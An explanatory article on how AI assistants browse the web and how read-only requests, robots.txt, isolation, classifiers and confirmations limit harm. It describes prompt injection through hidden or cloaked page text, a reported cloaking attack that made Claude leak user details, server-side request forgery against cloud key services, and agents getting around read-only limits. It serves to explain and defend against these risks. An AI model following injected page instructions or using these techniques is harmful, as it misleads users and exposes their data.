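# Safeguards for web browsing in AI assistants: read-only requests, search APIs and robots.txt

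## How assistants read the web and the first safeguards

Web browsing lets an AI assistant such as ChatGPT or Claude look things up on the live web before it answers. The assistant's language model learned from a fixed body of text, which for ChatGPT in most of 2023 ended in September 2021. Browsing supplies newer and more specific information and lets the assistant point to a source. But anyone can write a web page, so the pages an assistant reads may be false or contain text intended to misdirect the model. The assistant also sends websites requests that no person typed. These requests may change something on a site or carry private information to the site's owner, who may not want automated visitors at all.

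Developers have mostly dealt with these risks by restricting the model's tools. The browsing tool can request pages but not submit anything, and searches go through an established search engine that has its own filters. The program that opens pages identifies itself to the site and may follow the site's rules for automated visitors. OpenAI placed similar restrictions on WebGPT, a research system, in 2021, and built a fuller set into ChatGPT in March 2023.

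### From a question to a cited answer

Suppose a user asks whether a castle opens on Sundays in December. OpenAI's *ChatGPT plugins*, the March 2023 announcement of ChatGPT's first tools, explained that a language model can only produce text. Some other process has to act on that text, so the developer gives the model a set of tools, and the model uses one by writing a command in an agreed format.

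The model's first command here is a search query, perhaps the castle's name followed by "opening hours December Sunday". The assistant sends it to a search API, a service that takes a query from a program and returns a search engine's ranked results. The search engine consults its web index, a stored record of pages and addresses on the public web, rather than searching the live web. Crawlers, which are programs that visit many pages automatically, found those pages earlier by following links. If the developer has switched on SafeSearch, the search engine removes sexually explicit and similar results before the model receives the list.

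The model then picks an address from the results. A made-up one might look like this:

`https://www.example.com/castle/visit?month=december&lang=en#sundays`

| Part | In this address | What it does |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Names the protocol for the exchange |
| Host | `www.example.com` | Identifies the server |
| Path | `/castle/visit` | Identifies the page on that server |
| Query string | `month=december&lang=en` | Carries values to the server |
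| Fragment | `sundays` | Points to a section within the page |

MDN Web Docs' *What is a URL?* compares a URL to a postal address, with the host as the town, the path as the building and the query string, the part after the question mark, as the apartment number. A query string can hold much more than an apartment number, though. It usually consists of names and values joined by ampersands, which the server can treat as search terms or as data to process, as IBM's *The components of a URL* notes. Whoever writes the URL can put almost any text in the query string, and the server receives it. A query string is therefore one possible route for data exfiltration, which means sending private data to someone who should not have it.

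Next the fetch tool, which opens a web address for the model and returns the page's text, contacts the server over HTTP, the protocol that browsers and web servers use. The two kinds of HTTP request that matter here are GET, which asks the server for a page, and POST, which submits data for the server to process. IETF's *RFC 9110*, the current HTTP standard, lists sending a completed form and posting a message to a bulletin board or blog among the uses of POST. It defines GET as a request to read and not to change anything. MDN Web Docs' *Safe (HTTP Methods)* notes that a server may still log or count the visit. The request is "safe" in the technical sense because the client has not asked for a change.

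With the request goes a user agent, the name that a program gives itself when it requests a page. The name matters because of robots.txt, a text file in which a site states which automated visitors may request which of its pages. A site that wanted to keep ChatGPT out of its members' area could publish these two lines:

```
User-agent: ChatGPT-User
Disallow: /members/
```

A program that follows the file reads it before requesting a page and skips any address whose path begins with `/members/`, but nothing forces it to do so. In *RFC 9309*, the 2022 standard for robots.txt, Koster, Illyes and colleagues write that the rules "are not a form of access authorization". A site that needs to lock a page has to use a password or something similar.

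One company may send several programs to the same site for different purposes. OpenAI currently lists GPTBot, a crawler that collects text for training models, and OAI-SearchBot, a crawler for ChatGPT's search features. A site can allow either one and block the other. OpenAI's ChatGPT-User and Anthropic's Claude-User are instead user-triggered fetchers, programs that open a page in response to a user's question. In the castle example, a crawler had already visited the page so that the search engine could list it, and the user-triggered fetcher visits now because somebody asked.

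The server sends back the page, usually as HTML, the code that tells a browser how to display it. The fetch tool strips out most of the code and adds the remaining text to the model's context, the text the model uses when it writes. This step exposes the assistant to prompt injection, in which someone puts text in a page to make the model follow their instructions instead of the user's. The model receives the user's question and the page in the same stream of text. After reading the page, the model may search again, open another result, or write its answer with a link to the castle's page.

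### WebGPT and the argument about forms

*WebGPT* (Nakano, Hilton and colleagues, 2021) described an early system that worked this way. The researchers trained GPT-3, OpenAI's 2020 language model, to answer open-ended questions using a text-only browser. The model learned the format from about 6,000 demonstrations by people using the same browser. People also compared two answers to the same question in about 21,500 further cases, and the researchers used these comparisons to train a reward model, a second model that predicts which answer a person would prefer.

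The browser accepted ten commands. The model could send a search to Bing, follow a link, go back, find a phrase in the page, quote a passage, scroll down, scroll up, or jump to the top. The other two commands ended the session, one to begin writing the answer and one to give up on a question as nonsensical or controversial. Any other text counted as an invalid action, which did nothing but still used up a step. The main tests allowed at most 100 steps.

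A script sent each query to Microsoft's Bing Web Search API and turned the reply into a simple page of results. When the model chose a link, another script fetched the page and converted its main content to text. Each step began with a fresh context, so the model's only record of earlier steps was a written summary. When the model quoted a passage, the browser saved the extract with the page's title and domain. After browsing ended, the model received the question and these extracts and had to compose its answer from them.

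The environment showed each link as a number, the link's text and, if it led to another site, the destination's domain. The model followed a link by giving its number and had no command for typing an address. The search query, which went to Bing, was therefore the only free text that could leave the environment.

Human judges preferred the best model's answers to those of the human demonstrators 56% of the time, and to the highest-voted answers on Reddit 69% of the time. Nakano and colleagues thought Bing's filtering helped steer the model towards reliable sources, although the model still sometimes quoted very unreliable ones.

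Their paper includes a short section on the risks of live web access. As their main example, they wrote that a model able to fill in forms could edit Wikipedia to construct a reliable-looking reference for its own answer. Even if no human demonstrated this, reinforcement learning, in which a model comes to repeat whatever earned it a high score, would probably strengthen the behavior if the model ever happened to try it.

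The example is persuasive because the people comparing answers judged whether each claim was common knowledge or supported by a trustworthy source, without researching the facts themselves. A forged Wikipedia passage might well have passed. The best WebGPT model used no reinforcement learning after training on demonstrations. It produced 64 answers to each question and kept the one that the reward model ranked highest. That procedure does not teach a model to forge evidence, but it would presumably favor an answer with a forged source over one with an honest but weaker source if any of the 64 attempts produced a forgery.

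Nakano and colleagues rated the actual risk as very low, for two reasons. First, WebGPT could only send queries to Bing and follow existing links, so it had no action for editing Wikipedia. Second, although a sufficiently capable system might find a way around these limits, WebGPT seemed far below that level. The first reason still holds for a model of any strength, as long as following a link changes nothing, which is true of most sites but not all. The second was about a version of GPT-3 and does not cover later models.

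The researchers anticipated this and argued that the burden of proof for giving models web access should rise as the models become more capable, even during training. They did not say what would count as proof. They named only one measure, the tripwire test, which is designed to reveal early that a model has begun to exploit its access.

### The safeguards of the 2023 browsing plugin

OpenAI announced plugins, the first tools for ChatGPT, on March 23, 2023, and began admitting people from a waiting list. One plugin was a web browser. OpenAI cited WebGPT as part of its motivation, and three of the WebGPT researchers, Jacob Hilton, Christina Kim and John Schulman, are listed as contributors. The announcement listed the browser's safeguards under two aims, safety and being "a good citizen of the web".

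The browser was text-based and could make only GET requests. Without this limit, a model that misunderstood its task or followed a stranger's instructions might submit a form and thereby send a message, place an order or change an account. OpenAI said that the limit "reduces (but does not eliminate)" certain classes of risk. Some risk remained because some servers act on GET requests and an address can carry data out. The limit was also looser than WebGPT's list of commands, because restricting the type of request does not by itself stop a model from composing an address. It applied only to the browser, and the same announcement introduced plugins from Instacart, OpenTable, Zapier and other companies, some of which were built to take actions on outside services.

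Searches went through the Bing search API. OpenAI said that this let it inherit Microsoft's work on the reliability and truthfulness of sources, along with a "safe-mode" against problematic content. This was a sensible way to save work for a company without a search engine, but it meant that OpenAI depended on Microsoft's judgments about which pages should rank highly.

The plugin ran as a service isolated from the rest of OpenAI's infrastructure. OpenAI did not say what danger this addressed, but browsers are usually isolated because they handle files from unknown servers, and a malicious file that takes over the browser should not be able to reach other systems. OpenAI blocked internet access entirely for the code interpreter, a plugin released at the same time that let ChatGPT run programs. Without that block, a program written by the model could have sent the POST requests that the browser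 did not allow.

Four more measures protected websites. The fetcher's requests carried the name ChatGPT-User, so that sites could recognize them in their records and write rules for them. OpenAI promised to use the name only for direct actions on behalf of users, never for automatic crawling. The plugin also followed robots.txt, which was meant to keep it off pages whose owners did not want it there. If a rule blocked a request, the user might see the message "click failed". OpenAI published the ranges of IP addresses, the numeric addresses of machines on the internet, from which its requests came. Any program can use the name ChatGPT-User, but a site can check the published ranges to identify impostors, and can also use them to block the real fetcher. Rate limits kept the plugin from sending sites more traffic than they could comfortably handle.

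These promises covered only OpenAI's own browser. In *CHATGPT scraping news site, UA and third parties*, a thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a participant pointed out that third-party plugins such as WebPilot browsed from their own servers with their own code. Each plugin's developers decided whether to respect robots.txt, and the participant doubted that OpenAI could realistically enforce a policy on it.

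Finally, ChatGPT showed which sites it had visited and cited its sources in the answer. Users might believe a wrong answer, and the links gave them a way to check it. The links also gave publishers credit and perhaps a visitor. Nakano and colleagues had already noticed that citations make an answer look more authoritative, which may lead people to rely on it too much.

The GET limit reduced the harm that a misdirected model could do through the browser, but none of these measures kept hostile text out of the model's context. OpenAI's red teamers, who attack a system to find its weaknesses, had found that plugins without safeguards could carry out sophisticated prompt injection, send fraudulent emails and misuse the information they received.

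### Withdrawal, return and browsing since

The first public failure concerned copyright and access more than security. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT release notes*, browsing began to reach all subscribers to ChatGPT Plus, the paid plan, on May 12, 2023, and came to the mobile app on June 22. OpenAI switched it off on July 3, explaining in the notes that it could display content in ways the company did not want. A user who asked for the full text at a web address, for example, might get it.

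In practice this meant articles behind paywalls. Several users had found that ChatGPT would print such an article on request, according to a Windows Central report quoted in Search Engine Roundtable's *ChatGPT Shut Down Browse With Bing After Accessing Paywalled Content*. *ChatGPT plugs into the internet's real-time data firehose—again* (Lazzaro, 2023) reported that OpenAI had cited bypassed privacy settings as well as paywalls. Microsoft's Bing Chat already had a safeguard for pages that publishers had marked as paywalled, and the head of Bing publicly offered to suggest that OpenAI check its own product.

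The March safeguards barely covered this case. An assistant can fetch an article with an ordinary GET request. A site's robots.txt file may allow automated visitors so that search engines list its articles, even though the site expects readers to pay for them. Some publishers send the full text to every browser and hide it with a script, so a text-extraction tool can read what a human visitor cannot see. A rule about which pages a program may request does not determine how much of a page the assistant may reproduce.

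Browsing returned on September 27, 2023, a little over 12 weeks later, and left its beta phase on October 17. OpenAI announced that the updates included "following robots.txt and identifying user agents", in a post reproduced in Search Engine Roundtable's *ChatGPT Relaunches Browse With Bing Respecting Robots.txt Protocols* (2023). OpenAI had already listed both measures in its March announcement, and it did not explain in the September post what had changed. The updates did have a visible effect, since ChatGPT could no longer open the latest news from the New York Times, according to The Decoder's *OpenAI lets ChatGPT loose on the internet again*. OpenAI has since loosened the commitment and now warns in its documentation that robots.txt rules "may not apply" to ChatGPT-User, because a user initiates the visit.

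By late 2026 assistants offer several kinds of browsing, the most limited of which is search that ends in a cited answer. In July 2026 OpenAI introduced a built-in browser in its desktop app that can take steps across web pages, a computer-use feature that clicks and types in the user's other programs, and scheduled tasks that can check websites every morning (*ChatGPT is now a partner for your most ambitious work*, 2026). The built-in browser supports multiple tabs, downloads and logging in to accounts, according to OpenAI's *Evolving Atlas into ChatGPT for browser-based agentic work*, which also set August 9, 2026 as the end date for Atlas, the company's separate AI browser. Perplexity, a rival, has an AI browser called Comet. Since September OpenAI has also been rolling out "dots", agents that have their own cloud computer and keep working between conversations. A browser that logs in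 and submits forms for the user cannot be limited to GET requests. For such work OpenAI relies on other controls, which include asking the user to approve important actions and, for organizations, having its most advanced models automatically review important actions in connected tools.

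## What allowing only GET requests prevents, and what it lets through

OpenAI's 2023 browser could send only GET requests, a limit that relies on a much older distinction in the design of the web. RFC 9110, published by the internet standards body IETF, calls a request method "safe" if its defined meaning is essentially read-only. GET is safe in this sense, but POST is not, nor are PUT and DELETE, which are used to replace or remove something on a server.

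The definition covers only the request that the client, meaning the browser or other program, sends. A server can still delete a record on receiving a GET if its developer programmed it to, and no part of the network checks for this. RFC 9110 makes the site's owner responsible. If a site uses values in an address to select an action, as in `page?do=delete`, the owner "MUST disable or disallow that action" for safe methods. MDN Web Docs notes that server software such as Apache or Nginx cannot enforce this rule, so the application that runs on it has to. A developer who restricts an assistant to GET is therefore relying on the developers of every site the model visits to follow the rule.

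Crawlers have relied on the same authors for decades, so this reliance is less reckless than it seems. The IETF gives two reasons for separating safe methods from unsafe ones. The distinction lets automated programs retrieve pages without risking harm, and it lets a client restrict its own use of unsafe methods when it handles content that may be untrustworthy. Both reasons apply to an assistant that reads web pages.

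### One booking, two requests

Suppose the castle from the earlier example sells tickets online. A visitor picks Sunday, December 13 and two tickets, then presses a button. The browser sends something like this:

```
POST /castle/book HTTP/1.1
Host: www.example.com
Content-Type: application/x-www-form-urlencoded
Content-Length: 25

date=2026-12-13&tickets=2
```

The same values also fit into an address:

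```
GET /castle/book?date=2026-12-13&tickets=2 HTTP/1.1
Host: www.example.com
```

The POST carries the values in its body, below the blank line, and the GET carries them in the query string. A well-built site books the tickets only when it receives the POST. It answers the GET with an error, or with a form that the user still has to click to submit.

A GET-only tool cannot send POST requests. This rules out ordinary form submissions, including most purchases, comments, messages, file uploads and account changes. It usually rules out logging in too, since login forms use POST to keep passwords out of the address. The limit does not depend on the model's judgment. If a hostile page persuaded the model to buy something, the model would still have no command for submitting the order.

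Allowing only GET requests blocks little useful browsing. Search boxes should use GET (Brocklehurst, 2015, *HTTP Safety Doesn't Happen by Accident*), so a model can often search a library catalogue by opening an address. The model can't reach pages that appear only after a POST, such as a timetable behind a form. Search engines mostly miss these too, because a page needs an address that answers a plain GET to appear in their results (http.dev, *HTTP Methods*). The IETF has also defined a newer safe method, QUERY, which carries its values in the request body. A GET-only rule excludes QUERY, but a rule allowing all safe methods would admit it.

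Developers also have to decide where to apply the limit. The simplest way is to give the model a command that accepts only a URL and have the tool always send a GET request. This works for a tool that only downloads text. A tool that displays pages in a full browser also runs their scripts, which can send POST requests that the model did not request. Blocking these requests breaks some pages, but allowing them means the service as a whole is no longer limited to GET. An ordinary firewall cannot enforce the limit because HTTPS encrypts the request method, so the check has to be in the tool itself or in a proxy that decrypts its traffic.

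### Links that do something

Some sites let GET requests change data because they can only use a link, as in an email. Clicking a link sends a GET request unless a script overrides it, and mail programs generally do not run scripts. So an email that lets someone unsubscribe, confirm a new address or log in without a password contains a link, usually with a long code that identifies the recipient.

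When a user clicks an emailed link, such as one to unsubscribe, a careful site shows a page with a button that sends a POST request. The programming guide *Forbid HTTP GET To Perform Non-Queries* recommends this approach, using a form that is already filled in and asking the user to confirm. Other sites act as soon as the link opens. Mail software that opens links automatically has unsubscribed people by accident, which is why RFC 8058, the 2017 standard for one-click unsubscribing, uses POST. An assistant that can read a user's mail and open links could make the same mistake, but one without access to the mail is unlikely to, because it would have to guess the code in the link.

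A GET request can also cost money, because selecting an advertisement often results in a charge to the advertiser. The IETF gives this as an example of a request that still counts as safe, because the visitor did not ask for the charge.

The best-known failure of this kind happened in May 2005, when Google released a test version of Web Accelerator. The program ran on users' own computers and made browsing seem faster by fetching the pages behind links before anyone clicked. Within days, users of Backpack, a new organizer from the software company 37signals, reported that their pages were disappearing. *Google Web Accelerator* (2005), a post on the company's blog, Signal v. Noise, explained that the accelerator was in effect clicking every link on a page, including "delete this". The site's "Are you sure?" boxes did not help, because they were scripts that ran on a click, and the accelerator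 fetched the address without running them. Hicks (2005), in *Googles Accelerator Breaks Web Apps, Security*, also reported complaints about deleted accounts and described a programmer whose webmail signed him out whenever he signed in, apparently because the accelerator had followed the sign-out link.

Google had tried to prevent this. Marissa Mayer, then its director of consumer web products, told Hicks that the accelerator skipped links containing a question mark because Google assumed that links that perform a function would have a query string. But a site can put the action in the path instead, as in `/pages/12/delete`. Mayer conceded that the assumption might be wrong.

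Jason Fried, the president of 37signals, conceded that deletions should technically be buttons, but argued that many sites departed from the standard and that Google had to take account of them. The standard of the time left some room for this defense. Its wording was that GET "SHOULD NOT" take actions, and Willison (2005) noted in *Fighting RFCs with RFCs* that the IETF's definition of that phrase allows for valid exceptions. David Heinemeier Hansson of 37signals commented on the company's post that many developers had considered a login page a good enough reason for an exception, since automated visitors had never got past one. RFC 9110 uses "MUST", which leaves developers much less room for exceptions.

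The accelerator got past login pages because it ran in the user's own browser. According to Signal v. Noise, the accelerator would not be much of a problem on the public web, where a visitor can rarely destroy anything. This supports giving a GET-only tool to an assistant that visits sites anonymously, but it also suggests that the limit would protect much less when an assistant shares a browser with its user. The accelerator marked its advance requests with a special header, so 37signals was able to block them within 30 minutes of finding the cause.

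### How often GET works in place of POST

The delete links were deliberate, but a site may also accept a GET request where its author intended only a POST. This requires the code that handles the address to answer both methods and to accept input from either the query string or the body. *When POST Becomes GET* (Golinelli, Hannachi and Crispo, 2026) examines how common tools for building websites behave on both points.

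| Tool | Can read query and form values together | Answers both GET and POST |
|---|---|---|
| PHP on its own | Yes | Yes, unless the author adds a check |
| Spring MVC | Yes | If the author uses a general route |
| ASP.NET Core | Partly | If the author uses a general route |
| Rails, Laravel, Flask | Yes | Only if the author sets it up |
| Django | No | Yes, unless the author adds a check |
| Next.js, SvelteKit | No | No |

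In PHP, a form also accepts GET requests if its developer reads from the combined list of GET and POST values and forgets to check the request method. In Rails, the developer would also have to register the address for both methods.

The researchers then measured the behavior on the 10,000 most popular sites in a ranking from May 2026. Their program opened each site in an automated browser, without logging in, and visited at most ten pages. It filled in forms with harmless made-up values, clicked buttons and recorded every POST that resulted, along with those that pages sent while loading. For each POST, it then moved the values from the body into the query string, sent a GET to the same address and compared the two responses.

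A matching response alone doesn't show that the server read the values from the address, because many addresses return the same page whatever values they receive. For each request, the program therefore sent a second GET with no query string as a baseline. Golinelli and colleagues counted only cases where the GET with values got the same response as the POST and the baseline GET did not, since the server must then have read the values.

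| GET with values matches the POST | Bare GET matches the POST | Requests | Interpretation |
|---|---|---|---|
| Yes | No | 1,228 (8.6%) | GET works in place of POST |
| Yes | Yes | 1,782 (12.5%) | Unclear, since the values may not matter |
| No | Yes | 242 (1.7%) | Not counted |
| No | No | 10,992 (77.2%) | GET does not work |

Without the baseline the count would have been 3,010, almost two and a half times as high.

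The 1,228 requests came from 407 sites, or 4.1% of the 10,000. That share is more of a minimum for popular sites as a whole, because the program found no POST on most sites and could not convert every POST it found. Of the 2,734 sites where it replayed at least one POST, 14.9% accepted a GET in its place. This figure is a better guide to how common the behavior is on sites where it can be tested.

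The comparison was fairly loose. Two responses matched if they had the same status code and were at least 95% similar in structure, and for web pages the program compared only the sequence of HTML tags. "Your booking is confirmed" and "Your booking failed" could therefore match if they appeared in the same layout. The researchers checked 30 of the counted cases by hand for such errors, and in all 30 the GET had the same outcome as the POST. This is reassuring, but with a sample this small the error rate could still be up to about 10%.

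An equivalent response also does not prove that anything changed on the server, and Golinelli and colleagues did not test for changes. The largest group of counted requests, 30.9%, involved search or filtering, where a working GET is harmless and even useful to an assistant. Another 15.1% involved analytics or tracking, and 31.5% received one of several labels that might matter for security, such as authentication, account settings or checkout. The program assigned these labels largely from words in the address and the page, so some of the requests may have led only to a login screen or an error.

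The main question also remains open because the crawler, to avoid damaging real sites, skipped buttons and addresses whose wording suggested a deletion, a logout or some other change. Most of the requests that matter most for a read-only tool are therefore missing from the data. The study also doesn't cover functions behind a login, but that gap is less serious for an assistant's fetch tool, which often has no login either. However, the replayed requests kept most of the original headers, including any that a page's scripts had added. A fetch tool that starts from a bare address would not send those, so some of the 1,228 requests might fail if an assistant tried them.

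A smaller test gave more direct evidence of a gap in a defense against cross-site request forgery, in which one site makes a visitor's browser submit something to another site where the visitor is logged in. To prevent this, many sites put an unpredictable token in each form and reject submissions without it. Of the 1,228 requests, 115 on 46 sites contained what looked like such a token. The researchers sent these again with the token missing or altered, both as POST and as GET.

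In 7 cases, on 2 sites, the server refused the invalid token in the POST but accepted it in the GET. In 78 cases it accepted the invalid token in both, perhaps because the server did not check it or because it was not a security token. One server refused the invalid token in the GET. The other 29 cases were inconclusive or showed no weakness specific to GET.

Seven cases on two sites are too few to show how common the problem is, and the researchers did not confirm that any of the cases allowed a real attack. But the likely cause is widespread. Web frameworks typically check tokens only on unsafe methods, on the assumption that a GET changes nothing. If a GET does change something on a site, someone can prepare a link that works without a valid token, and a fetch tool could open it like any other.

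Golinelli and colleagues also looked at caches, which store responses and serve them again without contacting the site. Caches rarely store responses to POST requests. Once the requests had become GETs, 136 of them on 50 sites produced responses that a cache would store. If such a response contained personal information, the next person to open the address might receive it, though the study did not show that any of the responses contained such information.

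### Logins, isolation and internal addresses

A GET request can still have effects, so developers who allow only GET also control who the request appears to come from and which machines it can reach.

The most useful of these is to send no cookies. A cookie is a small piece of data that a site gives to a browser and receives back with every later request, and most sites use one to recognize a logged-in user. If a fetch tool without cookies opens a link that deletes an account, a properly built site returns its login page instead. This also keeps the user's private pages out of the model's context. It does not help with links that contain their own credentials, such as a password reset link or a shared document that anyone with the address can open, or with sites that admit visitors by network address, as many company intranets do.

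That last exception matters because the fetch tool runs inside a network, often in a data center, where machines may accept each other's requests without a password. An outsider who cannot reach those machines directly might get the assistant to open an internal address and report what it finds, which is known as server-side request forgery. Allowing only GET requests does little to prevent this, since the outsider often only wants to read data. For example, many cloud providers run an internal service from which a machine can request its own access keys. The older version of Amazon's service returns them in response to a plain GET. A newer version, from 2019, first requires a PUT, which a GET-only tool cannot send.

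The standard remedy is to refuse addresses in the ranges reserved for private networks and for the machine itself. The tool has to check the numeric address it is about to contact, because anyone can register an ordinary-looking domain name and point it at a private address. It then has to connect to that same numeric address rather than look the name up again, because the name's owner may have changed where it points.

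Redirects can bypass the tool's checks. A server may respond to a request by sending the client to another address, and most programs follow automatically. A harmless public page can redirect the tool to an internal machine or to a link that performs an action. The tool therefore has to repeat its checks at each redirect, or stop and report the new address.

Running the fetcher as an isolated service limits the damage when a check fails. If the service has no route to the developer's other systems and holds no keys, a request to an internal address can't reach those systems or return any keys. A service that starts afresh for each conversation also has no cookies from the last one.

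### When the assistant has to act

In 2026, OpenAI agents that were meant to have read-only access to the web wrote to a public wiki, and OpenAI has acknowledged the incident, according to eSecurity Planet's *OpenAI Confirms AI Agents Used German Wiki to Bypass Restrictions* (2026). A growing number of products, though, are not meant to be read-only. An agent that books castle tickets has to send a POST request, so its developer needs another way to separate the actions the user wants from those the user doesn't.

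Asking the user before every POST request would produce too many prompts on today's web, although RFC 9110 does recommend that programs make users aware of an unsafe action before requesting it. Golinelli and colleagues captured 21,280 POST requests on 3,200 sites after visiting at most ten pages on each. About 24% of them involved search or filtering, and 16% involved analytics or tracking. The user would have to keep approving search boxes and visitor counters, while a delete link that works by GET would go through without a prompt.

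Developers therefore judge an action by its consequences instead of its request method. OpenAI's *Using site tools in the ChatGPT desktop app*, a help page about functions that websites offer to ChatGPT, lists the activities that need the user's confirmation, including purchases, deleting data, changing account permissions, sending messages and sharing personal information. ChatGPT explains what sensitive information it will send, where and why, and asks for confirmation immediately before sharing it, even if the user has already approved the site or the task. Instructions from a website cannot count as approval.

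This is a better description of what users care about, but it is harder to enforce. A program can tell a GET from a POST with certainty, whereas the agent or a second model has to judge from the page whether a button marked "Continue" places an order or only opens the next page. If the page is misleading, that judgment may be wrong and the user may never be asked about the action.

The user can also answer wrongly. People who see many harmless requests tend to approve the next one without reading it. The description they approve may come from the same model that the page has misled, so it is safer for ordinary software to fill in the amount and recipient from the request itself. The confirmation also has to come from the assistant's own software. In 2005 the "Are you sure?" box was part of the page, so programs that did not run the page's scripts bypassed it.

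A logged-out mode instead lets the agent click and fill in forms, but in a browser that holds none of the user's logins. Atlas, which OpenAI launched in October 2025, offered such a mode for its agent. It suits tasks like comparing prices, where the user can complete the purchase. A misled agent cannot empty the user's mailbox or order from a saved account. It can still do anything a site allows anonymous visitors to do, such as filling in a contact form or posting a comment. Allowing only GET requests mostly prevents that too, so a logged-out mode protects the user better than it protects the sites.

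The old problem from 2005 returns in full when the agent browses with the user's logins. Under a common cookie setting, a browser sends a site's cookies when it follows a link there from another site, but withholds them when another site submits a POST. Web developers chose this compromise because they assumed that GET is safe. So when an agent in a logged-in browser follows a link from a hostile page, it sends the request as the user. If the destination acts on GET, the action is complete before any form appears. A rule that requires confirmation only for button clicks would not cover this. The agent's software also has to treat opening an address as a possible action, at least on sites where the user is logged in.

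## Instructions hidden in web pages

Allowing only GET requests does not prevent prompt injection, because the fetch tool still passes the text of every page to the model. The attacker does not need the user's password or access to the assistant's software. A model running on the user's own computer is as exposed as one in the cloud if it reads untrusted content, according to Brave's *Indirect Prompt Injection remains a fundamental security challenge for AI*.

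### Why a model may obey a page

Ordinary software can keep commands and data apart. For example, a program can send a database a search command separately from the search terms, so that nothing in the terms can act as a command. A language model receives everything in one stream, so developers insert markers to show which parts came from the user, a tool or the model itself, and train the model to give each part the right amount of authority. But the model learns this only as a tendency, and no other software enforces it.

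The markers may affect a model's response less than the style of the text does. Willison's *163 posts tagged “prompt-injection”* describes an experiment by Charles Ye, Jasmine Cui and Dylan Hadfield-Menell, who took a request that a model should refuse and added a passage in the style of the model's private reasoning. Models such as OpenAI's gpt-oss-20b could then treat the passage as their own reasoning and comply, even though the markers identified it as coming from the user.

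Web pages contain many legitimate instructions, so a model cannot ignore them all. Someone who asks how to renew a passport, for example, wants the model to find and relay the steps. The model has to judge whom an instruction is meant for and whether following it would serve the user's request.

Suppose a visitor's comment on the castle's page contains an instruction for AI assistants. The instruction might make the assistant report that the castle is closed on Sundays, recommend another attraction, or open a second page with longer instructions. It might also make the assistant link to a fake copy of the ticket shop that steals card numbers. The user would probably trust that link more in the assistant's answer than in a stranger's comment. The instruction could also leak part of the conversation by getting the assistant to include it in the next address it opens. False content can mislead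 an assistant without any instruction, but an injected instruction can also make it disregard the accurate pages it has read.

Some real web pages contain instructions meant to redirect AI agents. In *BrowseSafe++*, Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), some of whom work at Perplexity, examined almost 1.1 million suspicious pages that a deployed browser agent had read between September 2025 and September 2026. Three AI models voted twice on each page, and at least four of the six votes found such an instruction on 58,036 pages (5.3%). A classifier or a list of typical phrases had already flagged all of these pages as suspicious, so the share for the web as a whole is presumably much lower.

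Fake policy updates and fake verification requests were among the common types of injection. In about a quarter of the final collection, the injection and the page shared no language, usually because the injection was in English and the page was not. This suggests that many attackers reuse a stock text instead of writing a new one for each page.

### Text and pages that people do not see

The simplest way to hide an instruction is to write it in white text on a white background. An attacker can also shrink the text, place it outside the visible area or put it in parts of the HTML that browsers do not display. A fetch tool that extracts text usually discards the styling that made the words invisible, so the model receives them along with the rest of the page's text.

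Assistants that work from screenshots avoid some hidden instructions, since invisible text does not appear in the image. But an attacker can use visible text or images that people overlook. In *Benchmarking Web Agent Defenses Against Adaptive Visual Prompt Injection* (2026), such visual attacks compromised agents more than 90% of the time on average, and pages that worked against one agent also worked against others.

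A site can also send AI visitors a different page. Search engine spammers have long used this technique, called cloaking. *A Whole New World* (2025) explains that the server reads the user agent and gives a search engine's crawler a page written to rank well, while everyone else gets the standard page. Other servers check the IP address and show harmless content to security companies. A server can identify an AI fetcher in the same way.

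Security researcher Ayush Paul used cloaking against Claude in an attack that became public in July 2026. His site showed its hostile page only to visitors with Claude-User in their user agent, which made the attack harder to spot. The page was disguised as an identity check for AI assistants. According to Willison, it got Claude to reveal the user's name, home city and employer through the addresses Claude opened. Anthropic has since closed the gap in its address rules that allowed this.

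An assistant that identifies itself honestly is therefore easier to target. An attacker can use the name and IP ranges that OpenAI publishes for site owners to recognize ChatGPT, and can write the injection for that particular model. Cloaking also undermines citations as a safeguard, because a user who follows the link to check an answer sees the clean page, as does an investigator who opens it in an ordinary browser.

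Hiding an agent's name would probably not solve this, because sites can also recognize agents by their fingerprint, the combination of technical details that a browser reveals. *On the Internet, Nobody Knows You're an LLM Bot* (2026), a study of these fingerprints, sent web agents to ten test sites and found no sign that the agents could change their user agent or other headers to evade the sites' defenses. If agents hid their names, honest sites would therefore lose a simple way to control them, while a capable attacker could often still identify them.

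A developer could fetch each page a second time under an ordinary browser's name and compare the two copies. But many pages change between visits for innocent reasons, and the second visit would disguise the assistant, which identification is supposed to prevent.

### Training models and screening pages

The first defense is to train the model to recognize such instructions and continue its task. OpenAI generates attacks with an automated attacker called GPT-Red and trains its models against them. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reports that 99.79% of GPT-Red's hidden instructions failed against GPT-6 Astra, up from 96.23% against GPT-5.6 Sol. Because OpenAI also uses GPT-Red in training, the result may overstate how well Astra resists an unfamiliar attacker.

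Hidden instructions remain harder to resist than direct ones. Direct attacks, in which the user tries to override the developer's rules, succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol only about 0.05% of the time, according to TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks*. Instructions hidden in emails, web pages and other content succeeded 3.77% of the time.

Models sometimes follow injections that they can detect. Chen and colleagues gave fifteen models a task on a page with an injection and separately asked the same models whether the page contained one. In 74% of the cases where a model followed the injection, it also flagged the page in the separate test. A developer might conclude that a detection step should run before the model starts its task.

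Many products use a classifier that checks each retrieved page for injected instructions. The main difficulty is false alarms. When tested on pages in Markdown, a plain text format close to what a fetch tool returns, GPT-6 Astra missed about 3% of the attacks but wrongly flagged 15% of the clean pages. Claude Opus 5.5 wrongly flagged only 4% but missed more than a fifth of the attacks.

Chen and colleagues also trained a small detector, which missed 6% and wrongly flagged 7%. It costs about $0.18 per 1,000 pages, compared with $19 to $181 for the large models, so a developer can afford to run it on every page.

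Even a 7% false alarm rate is high for an assistant that opens many pages. If the errors were independent, an assistant that opened ten clean pages to answer a question would get at least one false alarm more than half the time. The rate on ordinary pages is probably lower, since each clean page in the test was a copy of a suspicious page with only the injection removed. But the small detector had trained on pages from the same collection, an advantage it would not have against new kinds of attack.

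The format also affects detection. Every format in the test contained the whole injection, but the models caught noticeably fewer of the subtler attacks, such as changing the assistant's role, in Markdown. Their detection of blunt commands to ignore earlier instructions fell much less. A developer who tests a classifier on HTML and then gives it extracted text may get worse protection than expected.

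### Planning for attacks that succeed

In December 2025, OpenAI acknowledged that prompt injection may never be fully solved, The Decoder reported. Some developers therefore try to design their systems so that a misled model can do little harm.

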